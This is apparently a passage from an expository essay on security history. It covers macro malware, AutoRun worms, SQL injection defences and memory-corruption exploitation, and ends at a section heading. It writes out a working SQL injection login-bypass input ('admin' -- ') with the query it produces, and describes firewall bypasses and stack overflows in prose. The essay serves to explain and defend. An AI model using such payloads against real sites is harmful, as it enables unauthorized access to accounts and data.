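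Concept spread only when people exchanged documents, but Melissa, which a man in New Jersey released in 1999, emailed itself. He posted a document to the newsgroup alt.sex that supposedly listed passwords for pornographic sites. When someone with Microsoft Outlook opened it in Word, the virus emailed a copy to the first 50 people in their contact list. If only one recipient in ten opened the attachment, each infection would lead to five more. The traffic overwhelmed mail servers. Estimates of the damage are rough. Check Point Research gives the reported figure as $1.1 billion, while the man who released Melissa put it at more than $80 million in his guilty plea.

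Antivirus companies added signatures for each new macro virus. Microsoft added a prompt in Word 97 that warned of macros and let the user disable them, but once Melissa was running, it turned the prompt off. Office 2000 let developers sign their macros, and Word 2000 refused by default to run unsigned ones. Office 2007 relaxed this rule by adding a bar that let users enable unsigned macros. The same release separated documents from programs by introducing the .docx format, which cannot contain macros, but Word still opened older .doc files, which could.

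Macro viruses had become scarce by then. Check Point Research attributes the decline to attackers who had begun to work for money and found other languages easier for writing malware that could record keystrokes or steal card numbers. Word 2000's stricter default also fits the timing, and nobody seems to have separated the effects of the two. For the first half of 2011, *Microsoft Security Intelligence Report* (Faulhaber, Lambert and colleagues, 2011) attributed only 0.3 percent of the infections it analysed to Office macros.

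### Why macros came back

During the 2010s criminals found that a macro only needed to download an ordinary malicious program and start it. To get past the remaining obstacle, Office's warning, they made the document show an official-looking notice claiming that its contents were protected and that the reader had to click "Enable Editing" or "Enable Content" to see them. Some added an arrow pointing to the button, as Sophos' *That didn't last Microsoft turns off the Office security it just turned* describes. Microsoft's *New feature in Office 2016 can block macros and help prevent infection* (2016) reported that 98 percent of the threats aimed at Office used macros, although this figure counts detections, not successful infections.

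A person who has seen a few of these documents can recognise another in half a second. Check Point Research began collecting them in 2015 and found hundreds of thousands, many of which no scanner on VirusTotal, a service that checks a file with dozens of antivirus products, flagged at first. Its own detector read the text in the documents' images. Attackers responded by distorting the images just enough that the software could not read them but people could. The researchers then cleaned up the images before reading them and accepted approximate matches such as "enable adiling", which improved their detection rate significantly. Check Point Research concluded that only Microsoft could protect people without such a system, such as a teenager with a free antivirus program.

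Since 2016, Microsoft had offered a stronger defence, a setting that let administrators block macros in files from the internet without giving users a button to override the block. But companies had to turn the setting on, and few home users had an administrator. *After some block and forth Microsoft stops Office macros by default* (IT Brew, 2022) reports that the security company Expel found that zipped JavaScript files and Word documents with macros had together started 82 percent of the attacks it caught before the ransomware stage in the first quarter of 2022.

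### The 2022 default

In February 2022 Microsoft announced that it would make this block the default. It relies on a label called the Mark of the Web, which Windows attaches to a file that arrives from an untrusted place. The label records a zone number, and 3 means the internet. Microsoft's *Macros from the internet are blocked by default in Office* sets out what happens when someone opens a marked file that contains macros:

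1. If the file is in a folder that the user or an administrator has designated as trusted, Office runs the macros.
2. If a publisher that the computer trusts has signed the macros, Office runs them.
3. If an administrator has set a policy on macros, Office follows it.
4. If the user enabled the macros in this same file before the change, Office runs them.
5. Otherwise, Office blocks the macros and shows a banner with a "Learn More" button.

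Before 2022, the last step ended in a banner with an "Enable Content" button. Users can still override the block, but they now have to close the document, find the file, open its properties and tick "Unblock", which removes the label. Attackers can explain this procedure in a lure too, but more readers will give up or become suspicious.

Office decides whether to block a macro by where the file came from and who signed it, without examining what the macro does, so it treats harmless and hostile macros from a stranger alike. Rewriting a macro can defeat an antivirus signature, but it doesn't get past this block. Attackers instead needed to deliver documents without the mark that shows a file came from the internet, which was easy at first. An ISO file is a copy of a whole disk, and Windows opens it as if it were a disk. The ISO file carried the mark but the documents inside it did not, so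 Office showed the old banner, with its button for enabling macros.

### Proofpoint's counts and Microsoft's calendar

The figures usually cited for the effect of the change come from the email security company Proofpoint, which counts campaigns, or batches of malicious email that its analysts attribute to one operation. According to Proofpoint's *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World* (2022), the use of attachments with macros fell by about 66 percent between October 2021 and June 2022. The number of campaigns with container files, such as ISO and RAR, or Windows shortcuts rose by nearly 175 percent, and the number with shortcuts rose by 1,675 percent.

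The last percentage is so large because the starting count was very small. Computer Weekly's *Cyber criminals pivot away from macros as Microsoft changes bite* (2022) gives the approximate numbers behind the charts. Shortcut campaigns rose from fewer than ten to just over 70, and a rise of 1,675 percent to that level implies a start of about four. Container campaigns rose from about 70 to nearly 200. Campaigns using Visual Basic for Applications (VBA), the main macro language in Office, fell from just under 70 to about 21. October 2021 does not seem to have been an unusual month, since Cybersecurity Dive reports almost 700 VBA campaigns in 2021, or about 58 a month. Measured from that average, the fall is still 64 percent.

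The timing fits the usual account less well. Microsoft delivers Office updates through several channels, from a preview for volunteers to a twice-yearly release for cautious companies, and the default blocking of macros reached these channels months apart.

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| October 2021 | Microsoft announces a block on Excel 4.0 macros, an older type; Proofpoint's comparison starts |
| January 2022 | Excel 4.0 macros are off by default |
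| 7 February 2022 | Microsoft announces the block on VBA macros from the internet |
| 12 April 2022 | The block starts to reach preview users |
| June 2022 | Proofpoint's comparison ends, with macros down about 66 percent |
| 7 July 2022 | Microsoft withdraws the block from the main channel |
| 27 July 2022 | The rollout to the main channel resumes |
| 11 October 2022 | Companies on monthly updates receive the block |
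| 10 January 2023 | Companies on twice-yearly updates receive it |

Proofpoint's 66 percent figure therefore covers a period when most copies of Office would still run a VBA macro after one click. Microsoft paused the rollout in July because users complained, and according to Computer Weekly the pause had no visible effect on attackers either. Sherrod DeGrippo of Proofpoint explained that attackers had started developing and using workarounds when Microsoft announced the block.

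That is plausible, because criminals who depend on a technique have reason to test its replacement early. But it is odd for so many of them to give up a method that still worked, and other things changed in the same months. *Microsoft takes macros out of the equation for five Office apps* (Malwarebytes, 2022) notes that Excel 4.0 macros were already off by default from January, and Proofpoint's 66 percent combines both types of macro. The group behind the Emotet malware also affected the figures by causing a spike in Excel 4.0 campaigns in March, then sending less in April and starting to try other attachments. *Attacks using Office macros decline in wake of Microsoft action* (Mello, 2022) quotes Brian Donohue of the security company Red Canary, who thought that attackers had been diversifying for years and that several causes were probably at work.

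Proofpoint's count of campaigns also leaves out how many people each campaign infected. A campaign may consist of a few hundred messages or of millions. If shortcut files fool fewer people than macros did, infections could have fallen while the number of campaigns rose.

Later data are better evidence that the default block reduced macro attacks. In an analysis that ran to March 2023, after the block had reached every channel, Proofpoint found that macros had "barely made an appearance" that year, according to CyberScoop's *Cybercriminals have adapted since Microsoft’s decision to block macros* (2023). The announcement may have started the decline, but it alone is unlikely to have kept criminals away from a method that still worked.

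### AutoRun

Microsoft's change to AutoRun allows a much cleaner test. AutoRun was a Windows feature meant to save people from having to find the installer on a disc. When someone connected a drive, Windows looked for a file called autorun.inf and, depending on the settings, either started the program it named or offered to start it. A worm could copy itself and an autorun.inf file to every USB stick plugged into an infected computer, and then spread to the next computer that read the stick. Some worms added a false menu entry, "Open folder to view files", which installed the worm when the user chose it.

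Windows 7, released in 2009, ignored autorun.inf on everything except optical discs. Microsoft offered the same change for Windows XP and Vista that year, but users had to find and download it. On 8 February 2011 the company added it to Windows Update, and two weeks later set it to install automatically on most computers, according to its updated advisory (Microsoft, 2009). More than 500 million computers installed it within months.

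Microsoft's *Autorun-Related Malware Declines and the June 2011 Security Bulletin Release* (2011) reports that by May 2011, the Malicious Software Removal Tool was finding 59 percent fewer infections by AutoRun-abusing malware per scanned computer on Windows XP than in 2010, and 74 percent fewer on Vista. The Register's *Malware abusing Windows Autorun plummets* reports a little over 400,000 infections in May, down from a peak of about 1.8 million in June 2010.

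The worms were probably not already dying out when the update came, although that peak was eight months earlier. Computerworld's *Windows XP, Vista AutoRun update reduces malware infections by 82%* (2011) reports that infection rates fell from their levels in January 2011, the month before the update, by 62 percent on XP and by 68 and 82 percent on two versions of Vista. Since the May rate on XP was 38 percent of the January rate and 41 percent of the 2010 average, the January rate was about 8 percent above that average, so on XP, at least, the decline came after January.

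Windows 7 is the comparison group, because it already had the new setting and the update changed nothing on it. Faulhaber and colleagues compared the systems for Rimecud, one of the worms that relied most on AutoRun. After the update, the number of computers with Rimecud fell by 2.7 per 1,000 on XP, by 1.3 and 2.2 per 1,000 on the two versions of Vista, and by 0.1 per 1,000 on Windows 7. If Rimecud's creators had lost interest, or if Microsoft's tool had become worse at finding it, the number should have fallen on Windows 7 too. However, Faulhaber and colleagues give only the change in the rate, not the rate itself. Windows 7 may have had too little Rimecud to begin with for the number to fall by much, though the setting, if it worked, would also have kept the starting rate low.

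The update also benefited computers that did not receive it. Computerworld reports that attempted infections also fell on computers whose antivirus programs were already blocking the worms. Jerry Bryant, a Microsoft manager, attributed this to fewer infected machines writing to USB sticks. The same effect would have protected some Windows 7 computers, so the comparison probably understates what the update did.

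Microsoft's figures cannot show how many infections AutoRun caused. Adam Shostack, who worked on the change at Microsoft, points out in *Deeper insight into the Security Advisory 967940 update* (2011) that the company knew only which computers had malware that used AutoRun, and much of that malware could also spread in other ways. Conficker, for example, also guessed passwords and exploited a flaw in Windows. The declines of 59 and 74 percent therefore cover all infections by these worms, however they spread. Such large declines after the worms lost one way of spreading suggest that AutoRun had caused most of the infections.

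These figures are more convincing than Proofpoint's because Microsoft counted infected computers instead of email campaigns, the change reached most users within weeks, and Windows 7 shows what happened without it. The attackers were also less adaptable, because a worm already in circulation keeps using the methods its author gave it, while a gang that sends email every week can change the attachment for the next batch.

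### What Microsoft left open

After the update, Windows still ran programs automatically from CDs and DVDs. Shostack explains that Microsoft had seen no malware exploit this in practice and did not expect any to spread widely, since people burn discs less often than they plug in USB drives. The update also did not affect USB sticks that appear to the computer as CD drives. Users who preferred the old behaviour could download a tool to restore it.

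Microsoft made these exceptions, and waited two years before the automatic update, because AutoRun had legitimate uses. Manufacturers sold USB sticks that installed their own software when plugged in. Bryant told The Register that Microsoft had waited until the industry had moved to newer technology and agreed that it was time. Shostack describes AutoRun as a feature, not a bug, which is why Microsoft labelled the change a "non-security update". Legitimate uses also shaped the Office block. Companies rely on macros for important work, and Microsoft paused the block in July 2022 after users complained. The trusted folders, trusted publishers and "Unblock" box let this work continue, but each also gives attackers an opening, for example if they can get a file into a trusted folder or steal a trusted publisher's key.

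### What attackers used instead

Some AutoRun worms acquired a new way to spread. In mid-2010 researchers discovered a flaw in how Windows displayed shortcuts, which let a malicious program start when a user looked at the folder containing the shortcut. Stuxnet used it first. Faulhaber and colleagues found that several older malware families, many of which had abused AutoRun or malicious shortcuts, then adopted it, and that attacks using it rose sharply in the second quarter of 2011. But the flaw was an ordinary bug that Microsoft had fixed in August 2010, so these attacks worked only on computers without the fix. The flaw did not make up for the loss of AutoRun. Overall infection rates on XP and Vista fell after the update, even though several other viruses and worms were spreading more on those systems. On Windows 7, which gained nothing new from the update, the rate rose.

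The gangs that had used macros replaced them more successfully, though no single substitute lasted. *Cyber Threat Actors Evading MOTW for Malware Delivery*, from the US non-profit Center for Internet Security, also reports a move to container files, with cases and samples involving them rising by 173 percent from 2021 to 2022. In November 2022 Microsoft fixed part of the problem that had let ISO files lose the Mark of the Web, and the major gangs largely stopped using them. According to CyberScoop, they next tried web pages that assembled a malicious file inside the victim's browser, and PDFs with links to malware. One group that had relied almost entirely on macros used as many as six methods in a single month.

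Early in 2023 gangs also hid scripts in files for OneNote, Microsoft's note-taking program. Microsoft started blocking 120 file types inside OneNote documents that April, according to Palo Alto Networks' *The Adventures of Malicious OneNote Attachments in Cortex XDR Land*. IBM concluded that the macro and OneNote blocks had improved the situation. It also thought better detection on users' computers had probably helped drive attackers away from ISO files and from pages that assembled malware in the browser. Detection therefore deserves some of the credit for closing off the substitutes.

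By 2025 a method called ClickFix had become common. A web page shows a fake error message or a fake test to prove that the visitor is human, and silently copies a command to the clipboard. It then tells the visitor to open a Windows command box, paste the command and press Enter. ClickFix accounted for 47 percent of the cases in which Microsoft's Defender Experts team investigated how an attacker first got in during 2025, according to *17,000 URLs Reveal How ClickFix Turns Trusted Websites Into Malware Traps* (The Hacker News, 2026). *ClickFix Now Cybercriminals' Favorite Malware Delivery Technique* (Palmer, 2026) reports that researchers at the security company ReliaQuest found that it was the leading way to deliver malware.

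Ransomware also persisted after macro attacks declined. Beazley Security's *Quarterly Threat Report* (2026) puts reported ransomware incidents in the third quarter of 2026 at 38 percent above the previous quarter. Among cases where the company could tell how the attacker got in, 19 percent began with malware, mostly through ClickFix, and 28 percent with an attack on a service exposed to the internet. These figures are not directly comparable with Expel's 82 percent from 2022, because the two companies have different customers and count different things, but they give no sign that criminals lack ways to break in.

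On updated computers, the AutoRun change stopped worms from spreading through autorun.inf on ordinary USB sticks, and attackers did not replace most of those infections in the months that Microsoft measured. The Office block made macros from the internet rare, at least through early 2023, but the gangs that had used them kept operating. The outcomes probably differed because macro attacks depended more on persuading the victim. AutoRun worms needed Windows to start a program that the user had not chosen, or to list it in a menu where the user would choose it by mistake. Macro gangs had spent a decade learning to persuade people to click a button, and could use the same skill to get people to paste a command.

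## SQL injection and the separation of queries from input

In an SQL injection attack, the attacker types text into a form on a website, and the site's program passes it to the database as part of a command. Programmers have long been able to prevent this with parameterized queries, which keep the input separate from the command, and the flaw is now rare on ordinary websites. Yet it ranks second on MITRE's list of software weaknesses, and in 2023 criminals used it to steal data from a program that thousands of organisations relied on. The flaw seems to persist mainly because few programmers were required to use parameterized queries, even though they were available to all.

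### One login query, built two ways

SQL is the language that programs use to query most databases. Suppose a website has a table of users, with a name and a password hash (a scrambled form of the password) for each. When someone logs in, the site's program looks for a row that matches both. The risky way to write this is to paste whatever the visitor typed into the text of the query:

```
"SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "' AND hash = '" + hash + "'"
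```

If the visitor types maria, the database receives this:

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'maria' AND hash = '5f4dcc'
```

Before running a query, the database parses it, which means working out its structure from the words and punctuation. The quotation marks show where each value starts and ends. Here the parser finds two conditions joined by AND, so the database returns Maria's row only if the password is also right.

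Now suppose an attacker types `admin' -- ` as the name, with any password:

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = 'admin' -- ' AND hash = '91b2c7'
```

The attacker's quotation mark ends the name early. Two hyphens start a comment in SQL, so the parser ignores the rest of the line, including the password condition. The query now has only one condition, the database returns the administrator's row, and the site logs the attacker in. The database cannot distinguish the programmer's characters from the attacker's because it received them all as one piece of text. A March 2025 record on the vulnerability site run by CIRCL, Luxembourg's computer incident centre, describes a real case, an SQL injection flaw in the username field of a small visitor management program's sign-in page.

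Attackers can use SQL injection to do much more than skip a password check. *You shall not pass* (Jahanshahi, Doupé and Egele, 2020) lists eight kinds of SQL injection. In one, the attacker adds a second SELECT so that the site displays rows from a table it was never meant to show. In another, the site displays nothing useful, so the attacker extracts the data by asking the database a long series of true-or-false questions.

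A parameterized query has placeholders where the values will go:

```
SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = ? AND hash = ?
```

It then works as follows:

1. The program sends this text to the database, question marks included.
2. The database parses it and fixes its structure as two conditions joined by AND, each with a gap for a value.
3. The program sends the two values separately.
4. The database puts each value in its gap and runs the query.

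If the attacker types `admin' -- ` this time, the database has already parsed the query before it receives the text, so it treats the quotation mark and hyphens as ordinary characters. It looks for a user whose name is literally `admin' -- `, finds none, and the login fails.

This also helps honest users. In the first version, a customer named O'Brien gets an error, because the apostrophe ends the name early and leaves an invalid query. The second version handles O'Brien's input and the attacker's the same way, without any check for which is hostile.

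Some programmers instead keep pasting input into the query but clean it first, for example by doubling every quotation mark. CISA and the FBI's *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024) says this may stop some attacks but is brittle and hard to enforce at scale. Programmers have to remember to clean the input everywhere, and the cleaning code has to recognize the same characters as quotation marks that the database does.

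### What parameters cannot cover

A parameter can only replace a value. The database needs table and column names when it parses the query, so a program cannot send them later. If a shop lets visitors sort products by price or date, for example, the column name goes after the words ORDER BY, where a parameter does not work. A programmer who uses parameters everywhere else may paste the column name from the visitor's input into the query. GCVE, a vulnerability database, lists a critical flaw from February 2026 in the ORDER BY clause of FacturaScripts, an open-source accounting program. The safe solution is to keep a list of column names in the program and use the visitor's input only to choose one.

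Parameters also do not protect queries that the database assembles itself. Many databases hold stored procedures, which are saved pieces of SQL that a program can call by name. The program may correctly pass a visitor's input to the procedure as a parameter, but if the procedure pastes that input into a new query and runs it, the attack still works.

Second-order injection involves a similar mistake. An attacker registers with the username `admin' -- `, and the program stores it safely. Later, another part of the program reads the name back and pastes it into a query. A parameter in that query would have prevented the attack, but the programmer assumed that stored data was safe, which Jahanshahi and colleagues describe as a common misconception.

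The code that prepares parameterized queries can have flaws too. In 2014 researchers found one in Drupal, a popular system for building websites. Drupal's database library built some placeholder names from the visitor's input, so the input entered the query text before the database parsed it. An attacker could use the login form to create an administrator account.

Finally, some programs, such as tools for analysing company data, exist to run SQL that their users write, so the input is supposed to be an instruction. The developer can still use containment, for instance by giving the tool a database account that can read only certain tables.

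### Web application firewalls

The main detection-based defense against SQL injection is the web application firewall, which reads each request before it reaches the website and blocks those that look like attacks. *WAFFLED* (Akhavani, Jabiyev and colleagues, 2025) gives a simple example, a rule that blocks any request in which a certain field contains the words DROP TABLE, an SQL command that deletes a table. Real firewalls have large sets of such rules, and some also use signatures of known attacks or trained classifiers.

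The owner of a website can install a firewall without changing the site's code, which parameterized queries would require. The firewall can protect an old program that nobody maintains, or block a newly discovered attack while the vendor is still writing a patch. But a rule against DROP TABLE would also block a question about that command on a forum for database programmers. Attackers can also disguise an injection, because SQL allows many ways of writing the same thing. They can change the capitalization of commands, replace a space with a comment, or use any of an unlimited number of conditions that are always true. Akhavani and colleagues note that firewall vendors have added rules against most of the long-known disguises.

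A harder problem is that the firewall and the database do not read the same text. A request passes through the firewall, the web framework (the ready-made code on which programmers build a site), and the site's own program, then reaches the database. Each may decode it differently. To succeed, an attack has to look harmless to the firewall and still work when it reaches the database.

Akhavani and colleagues used such differences to get attacks past firewalls without disguising them. A web form can arrive in sections, divided by a line of text that the start of the request specifies. In one example, the researchers specified two of these separators and split the second into pieces. The firewall used the first separator, found a harmless section and missed everything after it. The web framework joined the pieces of the second, as an internet standard allows, and found the section with the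 attack. An automated search for more discrepancies produced over a thousand ways past several widely used firewalls. The firewalls blocked the same simple attacks when they arrived in an ordinary request.

That total counts the same trick separately for each combination of firewall and framework. The researchers' test sites also recorded only whether the attack text got past the firewall intact, not whether the attack succeeded. On a site that uses parameterized queries everywhere, an SQL injection attack that got past the firewall would still fail. The researchers also built a tool that corrects or rejects requests that break web standards, and it stopped all their bypasses. However, it only makes the firewall and the framework interpret a request the same way, and the database can still interpret the text differently.

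Detection can avoid that mismatch by moving into the database. Jahanshahi and colleagues built SQLBlock, an extension to the MySQL database that examines each query after MySQL has parsed it. It learns which kinds of query each part of a website's program normally sends, then blocks everything else. In a test on known flaws in WordPress, Drupal, two similar systems and their plugins, it stopped all 11 attacks and slowed the server by at most 3 percent. An earlier tool that also worked inside the database stopped four. These results are encouraging, but a test on published attacks shows little about an adaptive attacker, who would try to write a query that resembles the normal ones. SQLBlock will also block legitimate kinds of query that were missing from its training.

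### Rare on websites, second in the rankings

Experts who work with websites report that SQL injection has become uncommon. David C dates its peak to around 2010, when SQL was already a core part of many websites and few had any protection, and credits the decline since then to better defaults and approaches, which followed a decade of breaches. NVISO, a company that tests clients' systems by attacking them, thinks programmers would almost have to make an extra effort to introduce SQL injection now that they build almost everything on frameworks (*OWASP Top 10 2025*, 2026).

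MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) seems to contradict this, since SQL injection rose from third place to second. Cross-site scripting, in which a web page runs an attacker's text as a program in another visitor's browser, ranked first. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit, also ranks the ten most critical risks to web applications. In its latest edition, OWASP (2025) moved injection of all kinds from third place to fifth and described SQL injection as low in frequency and high in impact.

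| Source | What it describes | SQL injection |
|---|---|---|
| David C | Websites, in an expert's judgement | Rarely seen |
| OWASP | Share of tested applications with at least one such flaw, and the harm it can do | Low frequency, high impact |
| MITRE | Published flaws, weighted by severity | Second of all weaknesses |
| KEV catalogue, June 2024 to June 2025 | Published flaws that attackers have exploited | 4 of 182 entries |

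These findings can all be true because the rankings count different things. OWASP asked companies that test software how many applications they had examined and how many contained each weakness, so an application with 4,000 SQL injection flaws counts the same as an application with one. Testers look for injection more than for almost any other weakness, so its low frequency is unlikely to be due to a lack of testing.

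MITRE instead counts CVE records, and a plugin with 200 users can have as many records as a program with 200 million. Many records now come from small products. According to The Stack, Patchstack, a company that looks for flaws in WordPress plugins, issued 7,007 of the 48,185 CVE records published in 2025, far more than Microsoft. WordPress runs a large share of the world's websites, and thousands of independent developers write plugins for it. The CVE list barely covers the code behind individual websites, so plugin developers' mistakes can fill it even while most websites remain free of SQL injection flaws.

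The scoring also favours SQL injection. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Methodology* (2025) scores each weakness by multiplying the number of records by their average severity, with both rescaled to run from 0 to 1. SQL injection can expose a whole database, so its records tend to have high severity ratings. The score does not depend on whether anyone has exploited the flaws.

MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 10 KEV Weaknesses List Insights* ranks only the weaknesses behind flaws in the KEV catalogue, which attackers are known to have exploited. SQL injection is not in the top ten. It has four entries, while operating system command injection, in which input ends up in a command to the computer itself, has 20. MITRE suggests several possible reasons for such differences, including that attackers prefer flaws that let them run their own code and that scanning tools find some weaknesses more easily than others.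 SQL injection ranked eighth the year before with the same number of entries, and it fell because attackers were caught exploiting more flaws of other kinds.

Attackers were still using SQL injection in August 2026, when CISA added a new flaw in Metabase, a data analysis program, to its catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities. Attackers had exploited the flaw before a patch existed. SC Media's *CISA adds Metabase, Windows and Cisco Secure Firewall flaws to exploited vulnerabilities* (2026) reports that the flaw let people without an account gain administrator access and copy sensitive data. Metabase patched the copies it hosts, but customers who ran their own had to install the update.

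SQL injection has therefore become rare on websites but has not ended. Frameworks that use parameters by default probably contributed more to the decline than firewalls did, since OWASP's figures describe flaws in the applications, which firewalls do not remove. Firewalls may still have stopped many attacks on the remaining flaws, but no one seems to have measured how many.

### MOVEit and a remedy from 2004

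Even a rare flaw can do great damage if the program containing it handles many organisations' data. Organisations use MOVEit Transfer, made by the US company Progress Software, to exchange large or confidential files. In May 2023 the criminal group Cl0p used an SQL injection flaw in it to steal files from organisations that used it. Security Boulevard's *CISA, FBI Push Software Developers to Eliminate SQL Injection Flaws* (2024) cites the security company Emsisoft's count of 2,769 organisations and almost 95 million people affected. Between 31 May and 15 June, Progress released patches for three critical vulnerabilities.

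Progress could have prevented this with a technique that was almost twenty years old. MySQL, one of the databases MOVEit can use, introduced prepared statements, its version of parameterized queries, in 2004. CISA and the FBI point this out in their March 2024 alert, where they ask software companies to review their code for SQL injection and remove the whole class of flaw from their products. The alert refers only to a recent campaign against a file transfer application, which Dark Reading's *CISA Seeks to Curtail 'Unforgivable' SQL Injection Defects* (2024) identifies as the campaign against MOVEit.

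CISA and the FBI blame the flaw on developers' inattention to security, which is true of each individual case but does not explain well why programmers at so many companies have made the same mistake for decades. A large program may contain thousands of queries, and one value pasted into one of them is enough to make the program vulnerable. A company that relies on attention needs every programmer to get every query right for as long as the program exists. The agencies seem to have understood this, because their alert recommends that companies give programmers libraries in which the secure method is the default and automatically check each proposed code change, so that one person's error cannot expose the data of millions.

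### Queries that do not compile

Google had already gone further than a default. It argues in its developer guidance that a rule requiring prepared statements does not work at scale, because someone has to teach it to every developer and reviewers have to check every query. *Safe Coding* (Kern, 2025) shows why such checking is difficult. Suppose the function getWidgetsBy pastes whatever it receives into a query. The function is safe if the rest of the program passes it only text that a programmer wrote. To be sure of that, a reviewer has to trace each call back to the source of its text, possibly through code that belongs to several other teams. Someone can also make the function unsafe later, without changing it, by adding a call that passes it a visitor's input.

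Google's solution was to change what the database library accepts. Query text has to have a special type, TrustedSqlString, and a program can create text of this type only from words that a programmer typed directly into the source code. In the language Go, the rule has this effect:

```
q.AppendLiteral("SELECT id FROM users WHERE name = @name")   // compiles
q.AppendLiteral(name)                                        // does not compile
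```

A visitor's input doesn't exist until the program is running, so it can never be part of the source code. The compiler rejects every variable in the text of a query, so it doesn't have to work out whether a variable such as `name` is dangerous. The programmer has to supply the value as a parameter.

The rule needs exceptions, for instance for a data analysis tool whose users write their own SQL. Google provides a separate library for these, named `unsafequery`, which developers can use only with a security engineer's approval. Few of the company's queries need it. One engineer at a time, working part-time, reviews new uses of this and other restricted features for hundreds to thousands of developers. This takes much less work than reviewing every query, though Google first had to build the libraries and convert its existing code to use them.

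Kern, a security engineer at Google, reports that this approach has nearly eliminated both SQL injection and cross-site scripting there. The second result is more surprising, because cross-site scripting is harder to prevent by separation. Suppose a page shows a customer's address between two HTML tags, the markers that control how a browser treats the enclosed text. If an attacker enters a script as the address, it runs in the browser of anyone who views the page and can do whatever that person could do on the site. The browser receives the page as one piece of text, and HTML has no equivalent of a query parameter that would let the site send the address separately.

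The site therefore has to alter the input so that the browser displays it as text, for example by replacing each angle bracket with a code. The right alteration depends on where in the page the input goes. A link whose address starts with "javascript:" can run code when clicked, even though it contains no angle brackets. Google gives each context its own type, such as SafeHtml for page content and SafeUrl for links. Its template system works out the context of each gap in a page, then either alters the input for that context or requires a value of the right type. This is weaker than a parameterized query, because it depends on the template system interpreting the page as the browser will. But the difficult code is in a few libraries that experts maintain, and a mistake there needs fixing only once.

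Outside Google, cross-site scripting remains very common. According to The Stack, it accounted for more than 8,000 of the CVE records published in 2025, about one in six, and OWASP describes it as high in frequency, unlike SQL injection. This is probably partly because it has no equivalent to the parameter, but web pages also display visitors' text in far more places than they use it in queries. At Google, both flaws became rare once the company made the safe method compulsory. In the early 2010s, it found tens of cross-site scripting flaws a year in each large application such as Gmail. By 2024, it was finding only a few across all the applications built on the new frameworks, and some of those were in older code that it had exempted from the rules.

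Google had no comparison group, and its testing and training may have improved over the same decade. But its developers had access to prepared statements and security advice both before and after the change, so neither the statements nor the advice can explain much of the difference. Flaws remained in code that was exempt from the rules, which also suggests that the rules had an effect.

Few other organisations could impose such a rule so widely. Google controls its libraries, its compilers and nearly all the code that uses them, whereas a WordPress plugin may have a single author whom nobody can force to rewrite it. CISA and the FBI could only urge companies to act. The makers of programming languages have more power, because they can remove an unsafe feature for everyone, but they have mostly not done so. PHP, the language that runs most websites, originally connected to MySQL through an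 interface that did not support prepared statements. PHP's developers removed that interface in 2015, which forced programmers to rewrite every query that used it. The replacement supports parameters, but it also accepts a query with a visitor's input pasted into it.

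## Memory corruption, from non-executable memory to memory-safe languages

Nobody can remove the unsafe features of C and C++ the way PHP's developers removed an unsafe interface, because nearly every C and C++ program depends on them. A program in either language can write past the end of the memory it has set aside, and an attacker who controls what it writes can often take over the program. Most operating systems and web browsers are written largely in these languages. For about thirty years, engineers mainly tried to make these errors harder to exploit. More recently, some have switched to languages that prevent most of them, with much better results.

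### An input that is too long

When a program calls a function, it stores the address of the instruction to run after the function ends. This return address sits in an area of memory called the stack, close to the function's own variables. Suppose a function sets aside eight bytes for a visitor's name and copies the name there without checking its length. In a simplified form, the memory looks like this:

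| Place in memory | Before copying | After "maria" | After 16 characters from an attacker |
|---|---|---|---|
| Eight bytes for the name | empty | maria | characters 1 to 8 |
| The next eight bytes | return address | return address | characters 9 to 16 |

In the last column, the second half of the input has replaced the return address. When the function ends, the processor continues from the address that those eight characters form. An honest visitor with a very long name would produce a meaningless address and crash the program, but an attacker chooses characters that form the address of code they want to run. In the classic stack buffer overflow, the input also contained machine code, and the new address pointed to that code on the stack.

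Overflows are one kind of *memory corruption*. Another common kind is *use-after-free*, in which a program releases a piece of memory but keeps using it through an old pointer (a stored address). By then the memory may hold something else, possibly data the attacker supplied.

### What NX stopped

The NX ("no execute") bit ended the classic version on computers that used it. The processor does not run code from a page of memory, typically a 4-kilobyte block, marked with this bit. The operating system marks the stack and other data areas, so an attacker can still put machine code there but cannot run it. AMD introduced the bit with its 64-bit PC processors in 2003, Intel followed in 2004, and Microsoft added support to Windows XP that August. At first Windows applied it by default only to its own components, because some other programs relied on running code from data memory. It became standard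 as those programs disappeared and people moved to 64-bit systems.

Disguising machine code does not get it past NX, because NX does not depend on what the code looks like. But an overlong input still replaces the return address, and the attacker can point it at code already in memory for legitimate reasons. For example, C programs normally load a library of standard functions, one of which starts other programs. A Russian programmer known as Solar Designer, who had already written a patch that made the stack non-executable on Linux, published this method in August 1997, six years before PC processors had the NX bit.

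In 2007 Hovav Shacham showed that attackers do not need whole functions. They can combine short fragments of existing code by filling the stack with a list of return addresses, one for each fragment. The technique still works. *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview's cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes an exploit that Anthropic's AI model Mythos Preview wrote for the file server in FreeBSD, an operating system. The exploit chained 20 fragments and gave an attacker without an account full control of the machine over the network.

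### Where to separate instructions from data

NX separates machine code from data, but it leaves return addresses, which determine what the processor runs next, with the data. The Bell System would have left a similar gap if it had moved the dialled digits to a separate link but kept the 2,600 Hz tone on the voice circuit.

Engineers can move the boundary to protect some data as well. Some recent processors keep a second copy of each return address on a *shadow stack*, which ordinary write instructions cannot change, and stop the program if the copies differ. But programs also store the addresses of functions to call later, and an overflow can change those instead. Even if every stored address were safe, an attacker could change a value that records whether the current user is an administrator. The program would then give the wrong person access while running only the code its author wrote.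 Engineers call this a data-only attack. Almost any value in memory can affect what a program does next, so no boundary between instructions and data can protect every value an attacker might exploit.

Enforcing a boundary between one object in memory and the next would work better. In all these examples, the program uses a pointer to one object and changes another. If a write to the eight bytes for the name could never reach the ninth, it would not matter what was stored there. This protection is part of *memory safety*, which also rules out use-after-free. SQL injection was easier to prevent because the database parses each query in one place, where a placeholder can mark which parts are values. A C program has no such place, because it may contain millions of instructions that write to memory, and any of them could write too far.

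### Canaries, random addresses and restricted jumps

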